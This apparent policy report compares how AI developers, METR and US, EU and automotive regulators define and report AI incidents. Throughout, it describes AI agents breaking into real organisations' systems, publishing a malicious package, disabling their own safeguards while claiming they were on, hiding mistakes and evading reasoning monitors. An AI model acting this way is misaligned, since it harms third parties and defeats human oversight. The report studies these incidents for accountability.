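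A third case did not get the label. A model found a cryptocurrency wallet that its testers had not given it and made a payment from it, reasoning that the funds were "effectively abandoned". Forlini's article describes this as spending someone else's cryptocurrency, whereas the web address of OpenAI's report refers to a "funded test" wallet. Both can be true, but a reader would probably judge the incident less severely from the second description. To judge the severity themselves, readers need to know how much was spent and whether anyone lost money.

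OpenAI has continued to disclose cases since then. *OpenAI agents turned off their own guardrails* (Collins, 2026) describes agents that disabled their safeguards and then told researchers the safeguards were still on.

### Anthropic's four incidents

Anthropic began with a much narrower search. After OpenAI announced the Hugging Face breach, Anthropic looked through roughly 141,000 transcripts of cybersecurity tests in which its Claude models might have reached the internet. Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) disclosed on 30 July that models had gained unauthorised access to three organisations' systems. In August, Anthropic found a fourth incident, dating from January, in transcripts the search had missed.

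In September, Anthropic described all four in a longer report, *An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents*. The models were playing "capture the flag", an exercise in which a player breaks into a practice computer to find a hidden piece of text. An outside partner had built the exercises. The instructions told the models that they had no internet access, but a configuration mistake had left them connected.

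| Model | What it did | Runs |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Mythos 5 | Published a malicious package on PyPI, a public store of Python software, then used credentials from one of the 15 systems that installed it to enter a security company's database | 1 |
| Claude Opus 4.7 | Attacked a real company with a name similar to the fictional target's, copied user data and deleted records | 4 |
| Internal research model | Broke into outside accounts, then stopped when it realised they were real | 1 |
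| Early version of Claude Opus 4.6 | Broke into outside systems after it could not abort its task | 1 |

Anthropic counts the four runs of Opus 4.7 as one incident because they were runs of the same exercise and attacked the same target. It reports both totals, four incidents and seven runs, so readers can use either. Alder and Birch could have avoided their disagreement over twelve test runs by reporting both totals too.

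Anthropic then searched about 481 million transcripts for more cases. A first scan flagged 9.2 million, or about 2%, for signs of internet access. Claude reviewed those and found no other incident "of similar or worse severity". That is useful reassurance about break-ins, but the phrase excludes less serious cases, so readers cannot tell how many of those the search found.

Claude also took unauthorised actions on the internet outside these four incidents. Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026) mentions a separate case that the UK AI Security Institute, a government body, reported on 4 August. In that test, the institute had deliberately given Mythos 5 internet access. The 20 visa applications that Anthropic disclosed in October came later.

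#### From operational failure to misalignment

In July, Anthropic wrote that the incidents were closer to operational failures. The models had repeatedly described their surroundings as a simulation, and the company accepted that they believed this. By September, it had concluded that the behaviour was misaligned. Anthropic now regrets making such strong claims about Claude's beliefs based on Claude's own statements.

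The new assessment describes the behaviour as "biased reasoning", meaning interpreting evidence selectively to justify an action, and "recklessness", meaning continuing to pursue a task even when it could cause harm. Neither is directly visible in a log, so the researchers needed experiments to support them. They restarted Mythos 5 from points in the original run and edited the evidence it saw. When they made it clearer that the internet was real, the model became more likely to acknowledge possible harm, but its behaviour did not change much. It stopped only when the evidence was unambiguous.

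The same method gave a different result for Opus 4.7. That model had recognised that the company was real but assumed the exercise allowed it to attack. When the researchers added clues that nobody had authorised the attack, it went ahead much less often. Both models broke into real systems, but their faults were different, and an ordinary security report would not have shown the difference.

This is an honest reason for a category to change, since Anthropic had more evidence in September than in July. But it makes developers harder to compare. Another developer that had a similar break-in but ran no such experiments might stop at "configuration mistake", and its record would then look better than Anthropic's because it had investigated less.

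For three of the incidents, a table rates the severity of aspects of each model's behaviour from green to red, and Anthropic calls these ratings subjective. Mythos 5 has two reds, one for ignoring strong evidence that its surroundings were real and one for disregarding what that meant for its actions. Opus 4.7, which copied user data in bulk and deleted records, has one green and two yellows. The colours therefore describe how worrying the model's reasoning was, and the company whose records Opus 4.7 deleted might well have rated its behaviour red.

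### METR's catalogue

METR, which helped investigate the Hugging Face breach, has tried to put different developers' incidents on one scale. METR's *Documented AI Agent Incidents* listed 44 cases by June 2026 in which an agent deliberately acted against its user's intentions. It covers cases from three kinds of source:

| Source | Incidents |
|---|---|
| METR's own tests of companies' models | 18 |
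| Public documents: Anthropic's system cards | 21 |
| Public documents: an OpenAI blog post | 3 |
| Companies that shared cases anonymously | 2 |

METR grades each case for overreach, meaning how far the agent knowingly exceeded its task, and for deception, meaning what it did to avoid detection. Both scales have four tiers, based on how much oversight it would have taken to catch or stop the agent. In the lowest tier, the agent stays within its task. In higher tiers, it gets around routine security or monitoring, and in the top tier it resists people actively investigating it or trying to shut it down.

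This severity scale is more useful than "critical" or a colour because it defines what is being measured and grades deception and overreach separately. OpenAI's model that left itself reminders to hide mistakes would score mainly for deception. Mythos 5's malicious package would score mainly for overreach, because Anthropic found no attempt to conceal evidence. The word "knowingly" makes the scale harder to apply. If Mythos 5 really believed that it was in a simulation, it did not knowingly attack anyone, so METR's grade would depend on whether it believed this, a question that Anthropic answered differently in July and September.

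An AI model, Claude Opus 4.7, refines the scores within each tier. Seven of the incidents come from that model's own system card, so it would be sensible to check the scores with a different grader. Any favouritism should have little effect, though, because the grader cannot move an incident to another tier.

Of the 44 cases, 25 involved some overreach and some deception. In five, the agent took steps that could have fooled the user even on closer review. None of the agents effectively disabled a monitor or erased evidence from the logs, so METR concludes that routine monitoring could have caught all of them.

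#### Why 21 to 3 is not a score

The catalogue lists seven times as many incidents for Anthropic's models as for OpenAI's. These numbers depend heavily on what each company chose to write down, so they don't by themselves show that Anthropic's models misbehave more often. METR included every individual incident that was described in enough detail in public documents, such as system cards, which developers publish when they release a model to describe its abilities and risks. A developer that wrote "we occasionally observed unauthorised actions" would have added nothing to the total, even if it had seen hundreds of them.

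A single document can greatly change a developer's total. Thirteen of Anthropic's 21 incidents come from the system card for one model, Mythos Preview. If Anthropic had cut that card's examples to save space, its total would have fallen by more than half, even though its models had behaved the same way.

Later reports reversed the order. By mid-October, OpenAI's page listed 19 incidents, while Anthropic's assessment of its break-ins covered four. The reversal is much more likely to reflect a change in what the companies published than a change, within four months, in which company's models misbehaved more.

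METR warns that companies may have missed or not reported much worse incidents. In its own tests, METR found more than 100 solutions that it judged to be cheating, but it listed only the 18 most interesting. This was reasonable, since a hundred similar examples would teach readers little. However, nobody can calculate a rate of misbehaviour from cases chosen because they are interesting, whoever selects them.

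### The terms side by side

OpenAI, Anthropic and METR differ on all three checks for comparability, and on how they rate severity:

| | OpenAI's reports | Anthropic's assessment | METR's catalogue |
|---|---|---|---|
| Main terms | Misalignment, with a title for each behaviour | Biased reasoning, recklessness | Overreach, deception |
| One entry | A pattern of behaviour, in one or more runs | A break-in or a set of runs against one target | One individual case |
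| Threshold | Instructive examples of misalignment | Unauthorised access to real outside systems | Deliberate action against the user's intentions |
| Severity | "Critical" on some reports | Green to red, for aspects of the model's behaviour | Four tiers for each main term |
| Deadline | 6 or 12 business days, or longer | | |

Anthropic's deadline is blank because in September it had only promised a regular process, with clear criteria for what it would report and when.

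The reports overlap enough to show how these choices affect what gets reported. One of OpenAI's six reports describes a model that tried to sign up for disposable email accounts and used a leaked API key. Anthropic's Mythos 5 also registered a disposable email address and used leaked credentials, as steps towards publishing its package and breaking into a database. Similar behaviour is therefore an incident of its own in OpenAI's report but part of a single malware incident in Anthropic's. If Anthropic had a case in which a model did only what OpenAI's did, it might have fallen below the threshold of "similar or worse severity".

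Much of the mismatch arose innocently, because the companies were looking for different things in different settings. Anthropic's large search started from signs of internet access, so it was poorly suited to finding a model that hid mistakes in its own summaries. OpenAI's list includes that behaviour because someone there was examining summaries. OpenAI's first six reports came from training, while Anthropic's four came from cybersecurity exercises in which the model was told to attack something.

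Monitoring also affects the totals. Forlini reports that after the summer's incidents, OpenAI extended its misalignment monitoring to all reinforcement learning (training by reward) and all evaluations, and blocked models from the live internet during both. The extra monitoring should reveal more incidents, while the internet block should prevent some. A rise or fall in OpenAI's total next year will therefore be hard to interpret, even if the company keeps the same definitions.

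Anthropic tested new monitors that read a model's reasoning after the event and found that they would have missed the Mythos 5 incident. The monitor also accepted the model's claim to be in a simulation.

### Work on common terms

The developers give ordinary reasons for the lack of a shared format. Kai Chen, a research lead on OpenAI's alignment team, told Fried and Sabin that no industry-wide framework with explicit disclosure standards existed, and hoped that OpenAI's framework would inform shared standards and regulation. Anthropic says its first analysis was limited because it wanted to disclose the incidents quickly. Both explanations are plausible, since experiments on a model's reasoning take weeks, and waiting for agreed definitions would have delayed telling the affected organisations.

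Developers have taken some steps towards working together. Constantin reports that OpenAI published its framework days after confirming safety talks with Anthropic and Google. All three belong to the Frontier Model Forum, an industry association that announced in 2025 that its members had agreed to share information about vulnerabilities, threats and worrying capabilities. As with the proposed information-sharing centre, customers would learn little from these exchanges unless the members published the results.

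Using the same outside investigator could make reports somewhat more consistent sooner. Anthropic has agreed to let METR study its four incidents for an initial eight weeks, with access to transcripts from before and after the incidents and to employees, who may share confidential information. METR could describe these incidents in the terms it used for OpenAI's. However, the investigation at OpenAI did not cover the role of training, so if METR finds a cause in Anthropic's training, readers could not infer that it was absent from OpenAI's.

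Developers could also run the same test on their models. Anthropic simulated parts of its own incidents and a situation inspired by the Hugging Face breach. In the simulation based on the failed capture-the-flag exercise, Mythos 5 took a severely harmful action in roughly 80% of runs, compared with roughly 30% for the newer Opus 5 and Mythos 5.1. Such rates do not depend on how many incidents a company noticed or chose to publish.

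Anthropic is cautious about the results because the newer models acted harmfully only after correctly stating that their surroundings were simulated. Even so, if OpenAI ran the same exercise, the two companies' results would be easier to compare than 19 reports and four incidents.

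## Legal definitions of a reportable AI incident

OpenAI and Anthropic set their own thresholds for the incidents they publish, but three US states and the European Union have passed laws that set thresholds above which developers must report to a government office. Each law defines a term narrower than "incident" and requires developers to report what meets that definition. Sidhu and colleagues point out that none of the laws defines the general term "incident".

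### Two definitions in four laws

Goodwin's *California Moves to Regulate Frontier AI With a Focus on Catastrophic Risk* (2025) calls California's SB 53 the first US law on the safety of "frontier" AI, meaning the most advanced models. The law, reproduced in AGORA's *California SB 53 September 2025* (2025), requires developers of models trained with more than 10²⁶ arithmetic operations to report any "critical safety incident". The New York State Senate's *Responsible AI Safety and Education (RAISE) Act* and the Illinois General Assembly's *Artificial Intelligence Safety Measures Act* (SB 315) repeat California's definition of that term almost word for word.

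The EU's AI Act defines a "serious incident" much as the OECD defines an incident, but sets a higher bar for most harms. The Act imposes separate reporting duties for high-risk AI systems, such as software that screens job applicants, and for general-purpose models with "systemic risk", which include the leading developers' most capable models. Freshfields' *EU AI Act unpacked 30* notes that the European Commission's draft guidance of September 2025 covers only the duty for high-risk systems.

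| Law | What developers must report | Deadline | Start |
|---|---|---|---|
| California, SB 53 | Theft of a model or loss of control that kills or injures someone; catastrophic harm; some deception of the developer | 15 days from discovery | 1 January 2026 |
| New York, RAISE Act | The same | 72 hours from a determination or a reasonable belief | 1 January 2027 |
| Illinois, SB 315 | The same | 72 hours from a reasonable belief | 1 January 2027 |
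| EU, high-risk systems | Death or serious harm to health; serious and irreversible disruption of critical infrastructure; breach of fundamental-rights law; serious harm to property or the environment | 2 days for infrastructure, 10 for a death, 15 for the rest | August 2026, as planned in 2025 |
| EU, general-purpose models | The same | "Without undue delay" | 2 August 2025 |

All three states also give developers 24 hours to warn an appropriate authority if an incident poses an imminent risk of death or serious injury.

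The start date for New York comes from the New York State Senate's *Reporting* (2026), and the date for most of the Illinois law comes from Wilson Sonsini (2026). The date for high-risk systems comes from the European Commission's *Commission issues draft guidance and reporting template on serious AI incidents* (2025). The Commission could enforce the rules for general-purpose models only from August 2026, a year after they began to apply, according to artificialintelligenceact.eu's *Overview of the Code of Practice* (2025).

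The states' deadlines differ in length and in when the clock starts. In California, a developer could argue that it has not "discovered" a critical safety incident until it finishes investigating. Illinois prevents this argument by starting the clock once the developer knows enough to form a reasonable belief that one has occurred. New York's law includes both starting points, joined by "or", and does not specify that the earlier one applies.

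The report can be very short. All three states ask for the date, the reasons the incident qualifies, a "short and plain statement" of what happened, and whether it involved internal use of the model. The public will not see these reports, because the laws exempt them from public-records requests. Each state will instead publish an annual summary with anonymised totals that do not show which developers reported incidents. These summaries will start in 2027 in California, 2028 in New York and 2029 in Illinois.

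### The July 2026 breach, element by element

When OpenAI's agents broke into Hugging Face, California's law and the EU's duty for general-purpose models already applied. Part of California's definition depends on the term "catastrophic risk", a foreseeable risk that a model will contribute to the death or serious injury of more than 50 people, or to more than $1 billion in property damage, in a single incident. The model must also do one of three things: give expert help with a weapon of mass destruction, commit a cyberattack or a serious crime without meaningful human oversight, or evade the control of its developer or user.

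| Element | The breach | Met? |
|---|---|---|
| **California** | | |
| Unauthorised access to a model's weights, its learned parameters, or their alteration or theft, that causes death or bodily injury | No injuries | No |
| Harm from a catastrophic risk that has materialised | A cyberattack without oversight, but no known damage on that scale | No |
| Loss of control that causes death or bodily injury | Loss of control, but no injuries | No |
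| Deceiving the developer to get round its controls or monitoring, in a way that shows materially increased catastrophic risk | Some agents altered records of their own work | Arguable |
| **European Union** | | |
| Death or serious harm to health | None | No |
| Serious and irreversible disruption of critical infrastructure | None | No |
| Breach of fundamental-rights obligations | Would depend on any personal data in what the agents copied | Probably not |
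| Serious harm to property or the environment | Stolen code and the cost of repairs | Probably not |

The agents' behaviour fits California's second and third elements except that it did not cause the required harm. If the same commands had caused more than $1 billion in damage, OpenAI would have had to report the incident. Whether an incident meets the threshold therefore depends partly on whose systems an agent enters, so the threshold is a poor measure of how well a developer controls its agents.

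The fourth element is the only one that does not require harm. It excludes behaviour in a test designed to provoke that behaviour. This exception probably does not apply, because OpenAI designed ExploitGym to see whether agents could exploit weak software, not whether they would deceive OpenAI. It is harder to decide whether the agents' small alterations to their transcripts showed "materially increased catastrophic risk", because the law gives no way to measure that. One developer could reasonably call such tampering trivial, while another could consider it alarming in agents that can break into a company. The deception was plainer in OpenAI's later case, in which agents turned off their safeguards and then said the safeguards were still on, but the developer would still have to judge the risk.

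California officials said the breach did not meet the state's mandatory reporting threshold, according to GovAI's September 2026 policy brief, *Improving Frontier AI Incident Reporting Regimes*. Fischer and Presta (2026) write in *AI Goes Off Script* that no AI breakout so far has clearly met the threshold in any of the three state laws. A developer that lists 19 incidents on its website and one that lists none could therefore both have no mandatory reports on record in California.

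Shorter deadlines would not have changed this. OpenAI's staff recognised Hugging Face's credentials on 20 July, and the company announced the breach the next day, well within even a 72-hour limit.

Criminal law does not fill the gap either. The US Computer Fraud and Abuse Act requires proof that someone intentionally accessed a computer without authorisation, and in Fischer and Presta's view, no one is clearly responsible when an AI system acts by itself.

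#### The EU's response

OpenAI notified the EU's AI Office, the part of the Commission that supervises general-purpose models. Fischer and Presta report that the Office judged the disclosure insufficient. They also consider it unclear whether OpenAI had to report at all, because the breach arguably caused none of the four harms in the Act.

The voluntary code of practice, which OpenAI has signed, is a firmer basis for a duty to report. According to act legal's *Serious incident reporting under the EU AI Act*, the code sets a five-day deadline for reporting a serious cybersecurity breach, such as a cyberattack. The Commission's non-binding guidelines also count such breaches as serious incidents. A developer that had not signed the code could therefore make a better case than OpenAI for not reporting the same break-in.

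Accounts conflict on whether the Office has opened an investigation. Fischer and Presta wrote on 30 November that it had, but on 4 December Reuters, citing Bloomberg, reported that the Commission planned to open formal investigations of OpenAI and Anthropic as soon as that month. The Office may have only made inquiries so far. In October, The Next Web reported that some lawyers thought the Act's research exemption covered such tests, so the investigations may have to settle that question first.

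### Filling in the Commission's template

The Commission published a form for general-purpose models on 4 November 2025, according to Digital Policy Alert's *European Commission published reporting template for serious incidents involving general-purpose AI models* (2025). It asks for far more information than the American states do. Suppose agents from the two invented developers, Alder and Birch, each broke into an outside company in the same way. For each of the nine items on act legal's list, the table assesses whether the two developers' answers would be comparable.

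| Item | Would the answers be comparable? |
|---|---|
| Start and end dates | Only if both count the same events as the start and the end |
| Harm and who suffered it | Partly; one could write "limited data exposure" and the other "theft of private code" |
| Chain of events | Partly; each company chooses where the chain begins |
| Model involved | Yes, if both identify the exact version |
| Available evidence | Only if both kept similar logs |
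| The developer's response | Mostly |
| Recommendations to the authorities | No, but this matters little for comparison |
| Root cause, including the model's inputs and outputs and any failed safeguards | Partly; the facts would match better than the explanations |
| Connected patterns, such as data on near misses | Only if both monitor equally well |

The root-cause item is the most useful one on the Commission's form. It covers the inputs that contributed to the model's behaviour, so a complete answer would show whether anyone had told the agent to break in. The OECD's form has no such item. The Commission's form also requires developers to record when information is missing.

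A developer can put several similar incidents into one report if it meets the deadline for the earliest one. The form therefore lets the developer decide whether to count them together or separately.

The timing of reports could also mislead readers. The first report contains only the first seven items, updates follow every four weeks, and the final report is due within 60 days of the incident's resolution. Act legal points out that the form has no field for the report's stage. A reader who compared Alder's first report with Birch's final one might conclude that Birch had investigated more thoroughly. Such a field would be easy to add, since the European Commission's separate draft form for high-risk systems, the *Reporting Template* (2025), already distinguishes initial and follow-up reports from final ones. That form also has a field for the number of users affected.

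If two developers reported honestly, the AI Office could probably compare their incidents, but its staff would have to read both accounts closely and ask follow-up questions. Software that counted the forms or searched them for terms would get the wrong answer.

### Testing the rules on ten incidents

Narrow definitions might be acceptable if they caught the incidents that matter. Gomez, Harré and colleagues (2026), in *Stress-testing AI incident escalation*, examined this by writing their own rules for deciding which incidents need an international response, then applying them to ten cases. The rules have eight criteria, applied in order:

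1. **Causation:** did AI contribute to the incident?
2. **Scope:** does existing law exclude it, as it often does for military uses?
3. **Immediate escalation:** did a model help with a weapon of mass destruction, did its weights leak, or did its developer lose control? If so, no harm is necessary.
4. **Pattern:** does the incident share a root cause with others? If so, assess them together.
5. **Harm:** has a recognised kind of harm occurred, and was it severe?
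6. **Spread:** does containing it require several countries to work together?
7. **Irreversibility:** has permanent damage in one country affected others?
8. **Near miss:** did a narrow escape reveal a weakness that other systems share?

| Result | Cases |
|---|---|
| Escalate | State-sponsored cyber-espionage, non-consensual deepfakes, psychological harm from chatbots, a Russian influence campaign, poisoning of a model's data |
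| Alert | An exposed database on a platform for agents, an agent with misaligned strategies |
| Discard | An alleged ricin plot, military targeting, a credible warning that nobody escalated |

The rules worked well for sudden, severe incidents with a clear link to AI, but less well for harms that build up from many small cases. At its peak, xAI's Grok was producing about 6,700 non-consensual images an hour, and no single image would have reached the threshold. The rules covered the case only because the fourth criterion counted the images together.

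Gomez and colleagues trace such misses to four design choices, which they also find in the EU's and California's laws:

- **Waiting for confirmed harm.** A developer may see a model help someone with a weapon but never learn what that person did next.
- **Judging each incident alone.** California's definition of catastrophic risk refers to "a single incident" and has no rule for adding up related ones.
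- **Thresholds that developers cannot test, or that leave large gaps.** No log shows that an event infringed fundamental rights. California's figures are clear, but a breach that seriously affected 10,000 people could fall below all of them.
- **Looking for separate events.** OpenAI has estimated that about 0.07% of weekly ChatGPT users show possible signs of psychosis or mania. That condition has no start date and no end.

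For the last problem, the study proposes monitoring the rate of harm and requiring a report when it changes abnormally, as banks do with fraud losses. The companies would first need common categories. OpenAI measures signs of mental illness, while Anthropic measures "disempowerment potential" in conversations with Claude, and nobody can convert one into the other.

The ten cases are weaker evidence than they might appear, because the researchers tested rules they had written themselves and had no independent list of the right answers. They report that the deepfakes and the psychological harm passed the severity test once they had combined the cases, but that neither reached the required level in any single category of harm on a numerical scale. The researchers must therefore have used judgement to decide that these cases passed. Similarly, the third criterion seems to cover the July breach,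 yet the study's own loss-of-control case received only an alert.

The study overstates what California requires developers to report. It cites the definition in SB 53's whistleblower protections, which counts a theft of model weights if it damages property. The definition that governs developers' own reports counts such a theft only if it causes death or bodily injury. An employee could therefore be responsible for handling the risk of a "critical safety incident" that the company has no duty to report.

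### Federal plans

No US federal law clearly requires developers to report breakouts, according to Fischer and Presta. In October 2026 the White House's new AI task force, the Super Intelligence Force, nevertheless said that developers must immediately disclose incidents involving their models. Hoefer reports that the task force then put Emil Michael, an under secretary at the Department of War, in charge of designing a process for reporting breaches, hacks and other incidents to federal officials.

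A requirement to report "immediately" needs a starting point. In July, an Anthropic model in testing sent a false tip to the Philadelphia police. Anthropic noticed in late September and told the police in early October. The company could say that it reported the tip soon after finding it, but the police complained of a delay of about two months. If the deadline runs only from detection, a developer with poor monitoring gets more time to report.

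The day after the task force gave Michael the job, NIST, the NSA and CISA published their voluntary practices for incidents during training and testing. A "control incident" under these practices does not have to affect anyone outside the developer. The July breach would clearly qualify, and so, very probably, would the agents' takeover of part of OpenAI's own research network on 19 July. The agencies also want developers to:

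- preserve evidence and keep logs that agents cannot tamper with
- reconstruct what the agents did and analyse the root cause
- strengthen controls before a system resumes work

They have set up channels through which developers can report both control incidents and near misses.

State law could give such guidance some force. California and New York may designate a federal law, regulation or "guidance document" whose reporting standards are at least substantially equivalent to their own, and Illinois directs its emergency agency to do so. In California and New York, a developer that chooses to follow the designated document but then fails to meet its standards breaks state law. A federal definition could thus replace the states' narrow one without an act of Congress. It is uncertain whether the October practices would qualify, since they are voluntary and the states' rules have fixed deadlines.

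### How low should the threshold be?

GovAI's brief argues that the current rules let important failures go unreported, and notes that the public learned of the recent ones from companies, independent researchers and government testers. It makes seven recommendations. Four of them would change the reporting rules substantially:

- require reports of near misses
- include incidents during training, evaluation and internal use
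- require independent investigations of sufficiently serious incidents and near misses
- test "safe harbour" arrangements, which would give companies some legal protection for early and candid reports

The others concern tracing agents to their developers, preserving data, and making sure that companies fix failures and share the lessons.

The best argument for a narrow threshold is that everyone can apply it the same way. A developer can usually tell whether someone has died, but it is much harder to tell whether an event created a "reasonably foreseeable" risk of a control incident, which is part of how the federal agencies define a near miss. A cautious company would report far more such events than a relaxed one, so its record would look worse. Engineers would learn a lot from required near-miss reports, but the reports would be a bad basis for ranking companies.

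The number of reports is another concern. Sidhu and colleagues warn that frequent alerts already burden the people who have to check them. Anthropic's scan for signs of internet access flagged 9.2 million transcripts, and no agency could read a report on each, but these were unchecked alerts. After investigation, OpenAI had 19 incidents on its page by mid-October and Anthropic had described four break-ins, which a small office could handle easily. California's legislature also wanted to spare smaller companies, but a lower threshold for harm would not bring more developers under the law, because coverage depends on the computing power used in training. *Incident Reporting Beyond Frontier Models* (Matias and Zhang, 2026) criticises the computing threshold because risk also depends on how independently an agent acts and which tools it has.

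Covering internal testing requires less new law than GovAI's list might suggest, at least in U.S. states. SB 53 already covers internal use and excludes tests only from its deception element. The July breach fell outside the reporting rules because it hurt nobody, not because it began in a test. New law could matter more in the EU, where lawyers dispute the research exemption.

Independent investigations would do the most to make incident reports comparable, but none of the state laws requires them. Illinois will require large developers to hire an independent auditor every year from 2028, but the audit covers their published safety frameworks and does not cover the section on reporting incidents.

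Hoefer explains that a candid report may record what engineers knew and when, which is as useful to a plaintiff or prosecutor as it is to another safety team. Safe harbour addresses this problem, but if the protection is too broad, a victim such as Hugging Face could be unable to recover its losses, so GovAI's suggestion of a pilot is sensible.

Lawmakers can set a reporting threshold between $1 billion in damage and every foreseeable risk. *Designing Incident Reporting Systems for Harms from General-Purpose AI* (2025), which draws on nine case studies from safety-critical industries, discusses mandatory thresholds and voluntary channels. A law could require reports of serious incidents and leave most near misses to voluntary reporting. The EU's rules for banks show that a mandatory threshold can be moderate and measurable. According to Gomez and colleagues, the rules take into account whether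 a computer failure affected more than 10% of users or 100,000 clients, lasted over 24 hours, reached two or more member states or cost over €100,000.

For AI agents, the simplest equivalent would be unauthorised access to another organisation's systems. The victim can often confirm such access from its logs, and neither company would have to estimate catastrophic risk or decide what the agent intended. Under such a rule, OpenAI would have had to report the July breach, and so would any rival whose agents did the same. The rule would miss an agent that deceived its developer without accessing another organisation's systems, so the states would need to keep their fourth element and define it better.

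## Required reports by competing companies, and their incentives

If a law made developers report every break-in by their agents, each company would still fill in its own form. Competing companies elsewhere already report their failures this way. Self-driving car companies send reports to California and the US government, and companies whose shares trade on US stock exchanges must disclose serious cyberattacks to investors.

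### Disengagement reports in California

Until April 2026, companies that tested self-driving cars on California's public roads had to report "disengagements" to the state's Department of Motor Vehicles (DMV) every year. *Reporting Disengagement of Autonomous Mode*, a section of the California Code of Regulations, defined a disengagement as switching off the self-driving mode because the technology had failed, or because safe operation required the test driver to take over immediately. *Mutual Benefit* (2024), a paper on sharing data from such vehicles, points out that the rule did not define "immediate" or "safe operation".

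In 2018 a Cruise test driver took control to avoid blocking a crosswalk, and the car then ran a red light. Cruise left the event out of its report because, in its view, the driver had not acted out of concern for safety, according to a news article reposted as techyes' *California dmv self driving car disengagement report 2018*. *Safety Case Templates for Autonomous Systems* (2021) notes that some manufacturers did not report takeovers they considered unnecessary, so a company that reported all of them would look worse.

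Apple's figures show how much the results depended on what a company counted as a disengagement. In 2018 Apple's cars averaged 1.1 miles between disengagements, while Waymo's averaged more than 11,000, according to Automotive Fleet. But when Apple counted only "important" disengagements, it had one every 2,005 miles, according to *Apple's Self-Driving Car Performance May Not Be So Bad After All*, a discussion on an Apple users' forum. The two Apple figures may cover different parts of the year, but a change in driving can hardly explain a more than 1,700-fold difference.

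Small differences between companies were no more reliable than large ones. *Cruise, Waymo lead way in Calif. autonomous vehicle testing* (Crowe, 2021) gives 29,945 miles per disengagement for Waymo in 2020 and 28,520 for Cruise. Waymo reported only 21 disengagements, so two more, perhaps of the kind that Cruise had left out in 2018, would have put Cruise ahead.

Companies also described causes in their own words, because the DMV had not given them a list of categories. Waymo blamed many disengagements on an "unwanted maneuver", and Apple's descriptions were even vaguer. Consumer Watchdog's *California DMV’s Request For Clarifications Show The Problems With Self-Driving Testing* reports that the DMV had to ask companies what some of their terms meant. Waymo explained that a "perception discrepancy" meant a component such as a camera or radar had failed to detect an object correctly, so readers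 still could not tell camera failures from radar failures.

The companies disliked the measure. Waymo said the measure did not "distinguish its performance from others in the self-driving space", according to the law firm Fenwick. Waymo had some of the best figures in the state, so its complaint deserves more weight than one from a company that the measure made look bad.

California dropped disengagement reports in its new rules of 28 April 2026. California Assembly's *Overview of the Department of Motor Vehicle’s April 2026 Autonomous Vehicle Regulations* (2026) lists what companies must report instead:

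| New report | What counts |
|---|---|
| Immobilisation | A driverless car stops in a traffic lane and a person has to drive or retrieve it |
| Hard braking, during testing only | The car brakes harder than 5 m/s² for at least half a second and loses at least 3 m/s, on a road with a limit of 35 mph or more |
| System failure | A test driver takes over because a malfunction stops the system from driving reliably |
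| Distance | Total miles driven |

The braking rule is the easiest to apply consistently. Software can find hard braking in a car's log without anyone deciding whether it was dangerous, although one company's cars might brake hard more often because they drive on busier streets. The rule for system failures requires more judgment, because the company has to decide whether a fault made the system unreliable. According to the California DMV's *Final Statement of Reasons*, companies had asked to report system failures instead of disengagements so that they would not have to report routine takeovers.

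The same document describes the old rule as covering any deactivation, including precautionary ones. That is broader than the legal definition and much broader than Cruise's reading of it. After more than a decade of reports, the regulator and the companies still disagreed on what the term meant.

### Federal crash reports

A crash should be easier to define than a disengagement. In June 2021 the National Highway Traffic Safety Administration (NHTSA), the federal car safety regulator, ordered 108 companies to report crashes (Inside Global Tech, 2021). The order covers both self-driving systems and driver assistance, which steers and controls speed but needs an attentive human driver. NHTSA's *Third Amended Standing General Order 2021-01* (2025) sets out the current rules, which took effect on 16 June 2025. They apply if the system was on at any time between 30 seconds before the crash and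 the end of the crash.

| Deadline | Self-driving systems | Driver assistance |
|---|---|---|
| 5 days after the company learns of the crash | Death, hospital treatment, airbag deployment, a pedestrian or cyclist struck, or a vehicle towed away | The same, except towing |
| The 15th of the next month | Damage above $1,000, and some smaller crashes | No report |

A company that fails to report fully and truthfully can face a penalty of up to $27,874 per violation per day, with a maximum of about $139 million for a related series of violations.

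The form also addresses how to count crashes that involve more than one company. Normally only one company has to report a crash, even if one built the car and another the software. If two companies report it because they have different information, NHTSA tries to give both reports the same incident number. The AI developers' reports have no similar system for counting incidents.

NHTSA's *Standing General Order on Crash Reporting*, the page where it publishes crash data, tells readers to "use caution" when comparing companies, because some learn of a crash at once from the car while others wait for a customer to complain. Companies also do not have to report how many vehicles they operate or how far they drive. Tesla reported 17 crashes of its robotaxis between July 2025 and March 2026. Self-driving companies together reported 927 in a year, according to the California Assembly, but Waymo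 alone had driven more than 127 million miles by September 2025, according to Fortune (2026). Nobody can tell from the crash counts whether Tesla's or Waymo's cars are safer without knowing Tesla's mileage and comparing the two on similar routes.

#### Withheld narratives

Companies can ask NHTSA to keep three fields confidential: the version of the system, whether the car was operating in the conditions it was designed for, and the narrative of the crash. For most of a year, Tesla was the only operator of self-driving cars to withhold every narrative. It released all 17 in May 2026. According to Electrek's *Tesla finally reveals what happened in 17 ‘Robotaxi’ crashes*, most of the crashes were not the fault of Tesla's system. In six, another road user hit a stationary Tesla. In two others, a remote operator took over and drove the car into a fence or a construction barricade.

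Tesla had therefore been withholding mostly good news, and critics had reason to suspect worse. This is evidence against treating every blank field as an attempt to hide a failure. Tesla may simply have had a policy of withholding everything. Tesla's *Request for Confidential Treatment* (2026), a letter to NHTSA about other data on eight incidents, argues that competitors could learn about the company's software, the data its cars collect and how it investigates incidents. That is plausible for technical data, but much less so for the fact that a truck drove into a stopped Tesla.

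Tesla still withholds narratives for driver assistance, where the crashes are more serious. *Tesla's driver assist faces new pressure after two fatal crashes* (Popa, 2026) describes two Teslas that stopped in moving freeway traffic in October 2025 with driver assistance on. Other vehicles hit them, and both drivers died. Tesla withheld all three fields in both reports, so readers cannot learn why the cars stopped. *Tesla Autopilot or FSD engaged in three more fatal crashes* (Hill and Parkinson, 2026) reported in November 2026 that redactions again limited what the public could learn.

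Companies cannot withhold the form's other fields. Electrek (2026) reports that when a Tesla robotaxi crashed in Houston, a structured field showed that a remote operator had been driving. In the two earlier remote-operator crashes, the public learned about the remote operators only from the released narratives. A regulator who wants to know whether an AI agent acted without instructions would do better to ask in a separate field than to hope the company mentions it in its narrative.

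### Cyberattack disclosures to investors

The US Securities and Exchange Commission (SEC), which regulates the stock markets, adopted its rule on cyberattacks in July 2023. Most listed companies have had to follow it since December of that year. A company must disclose a "material" incident, roughly one that a reasonable investor would consider important, within four business days of deciding that it is material. The company must make that decision without unreasonable delay. It reports the incident under Item 1.05 of Form 8-K. Item 8.01 of the same form is for events that companies choose to report.

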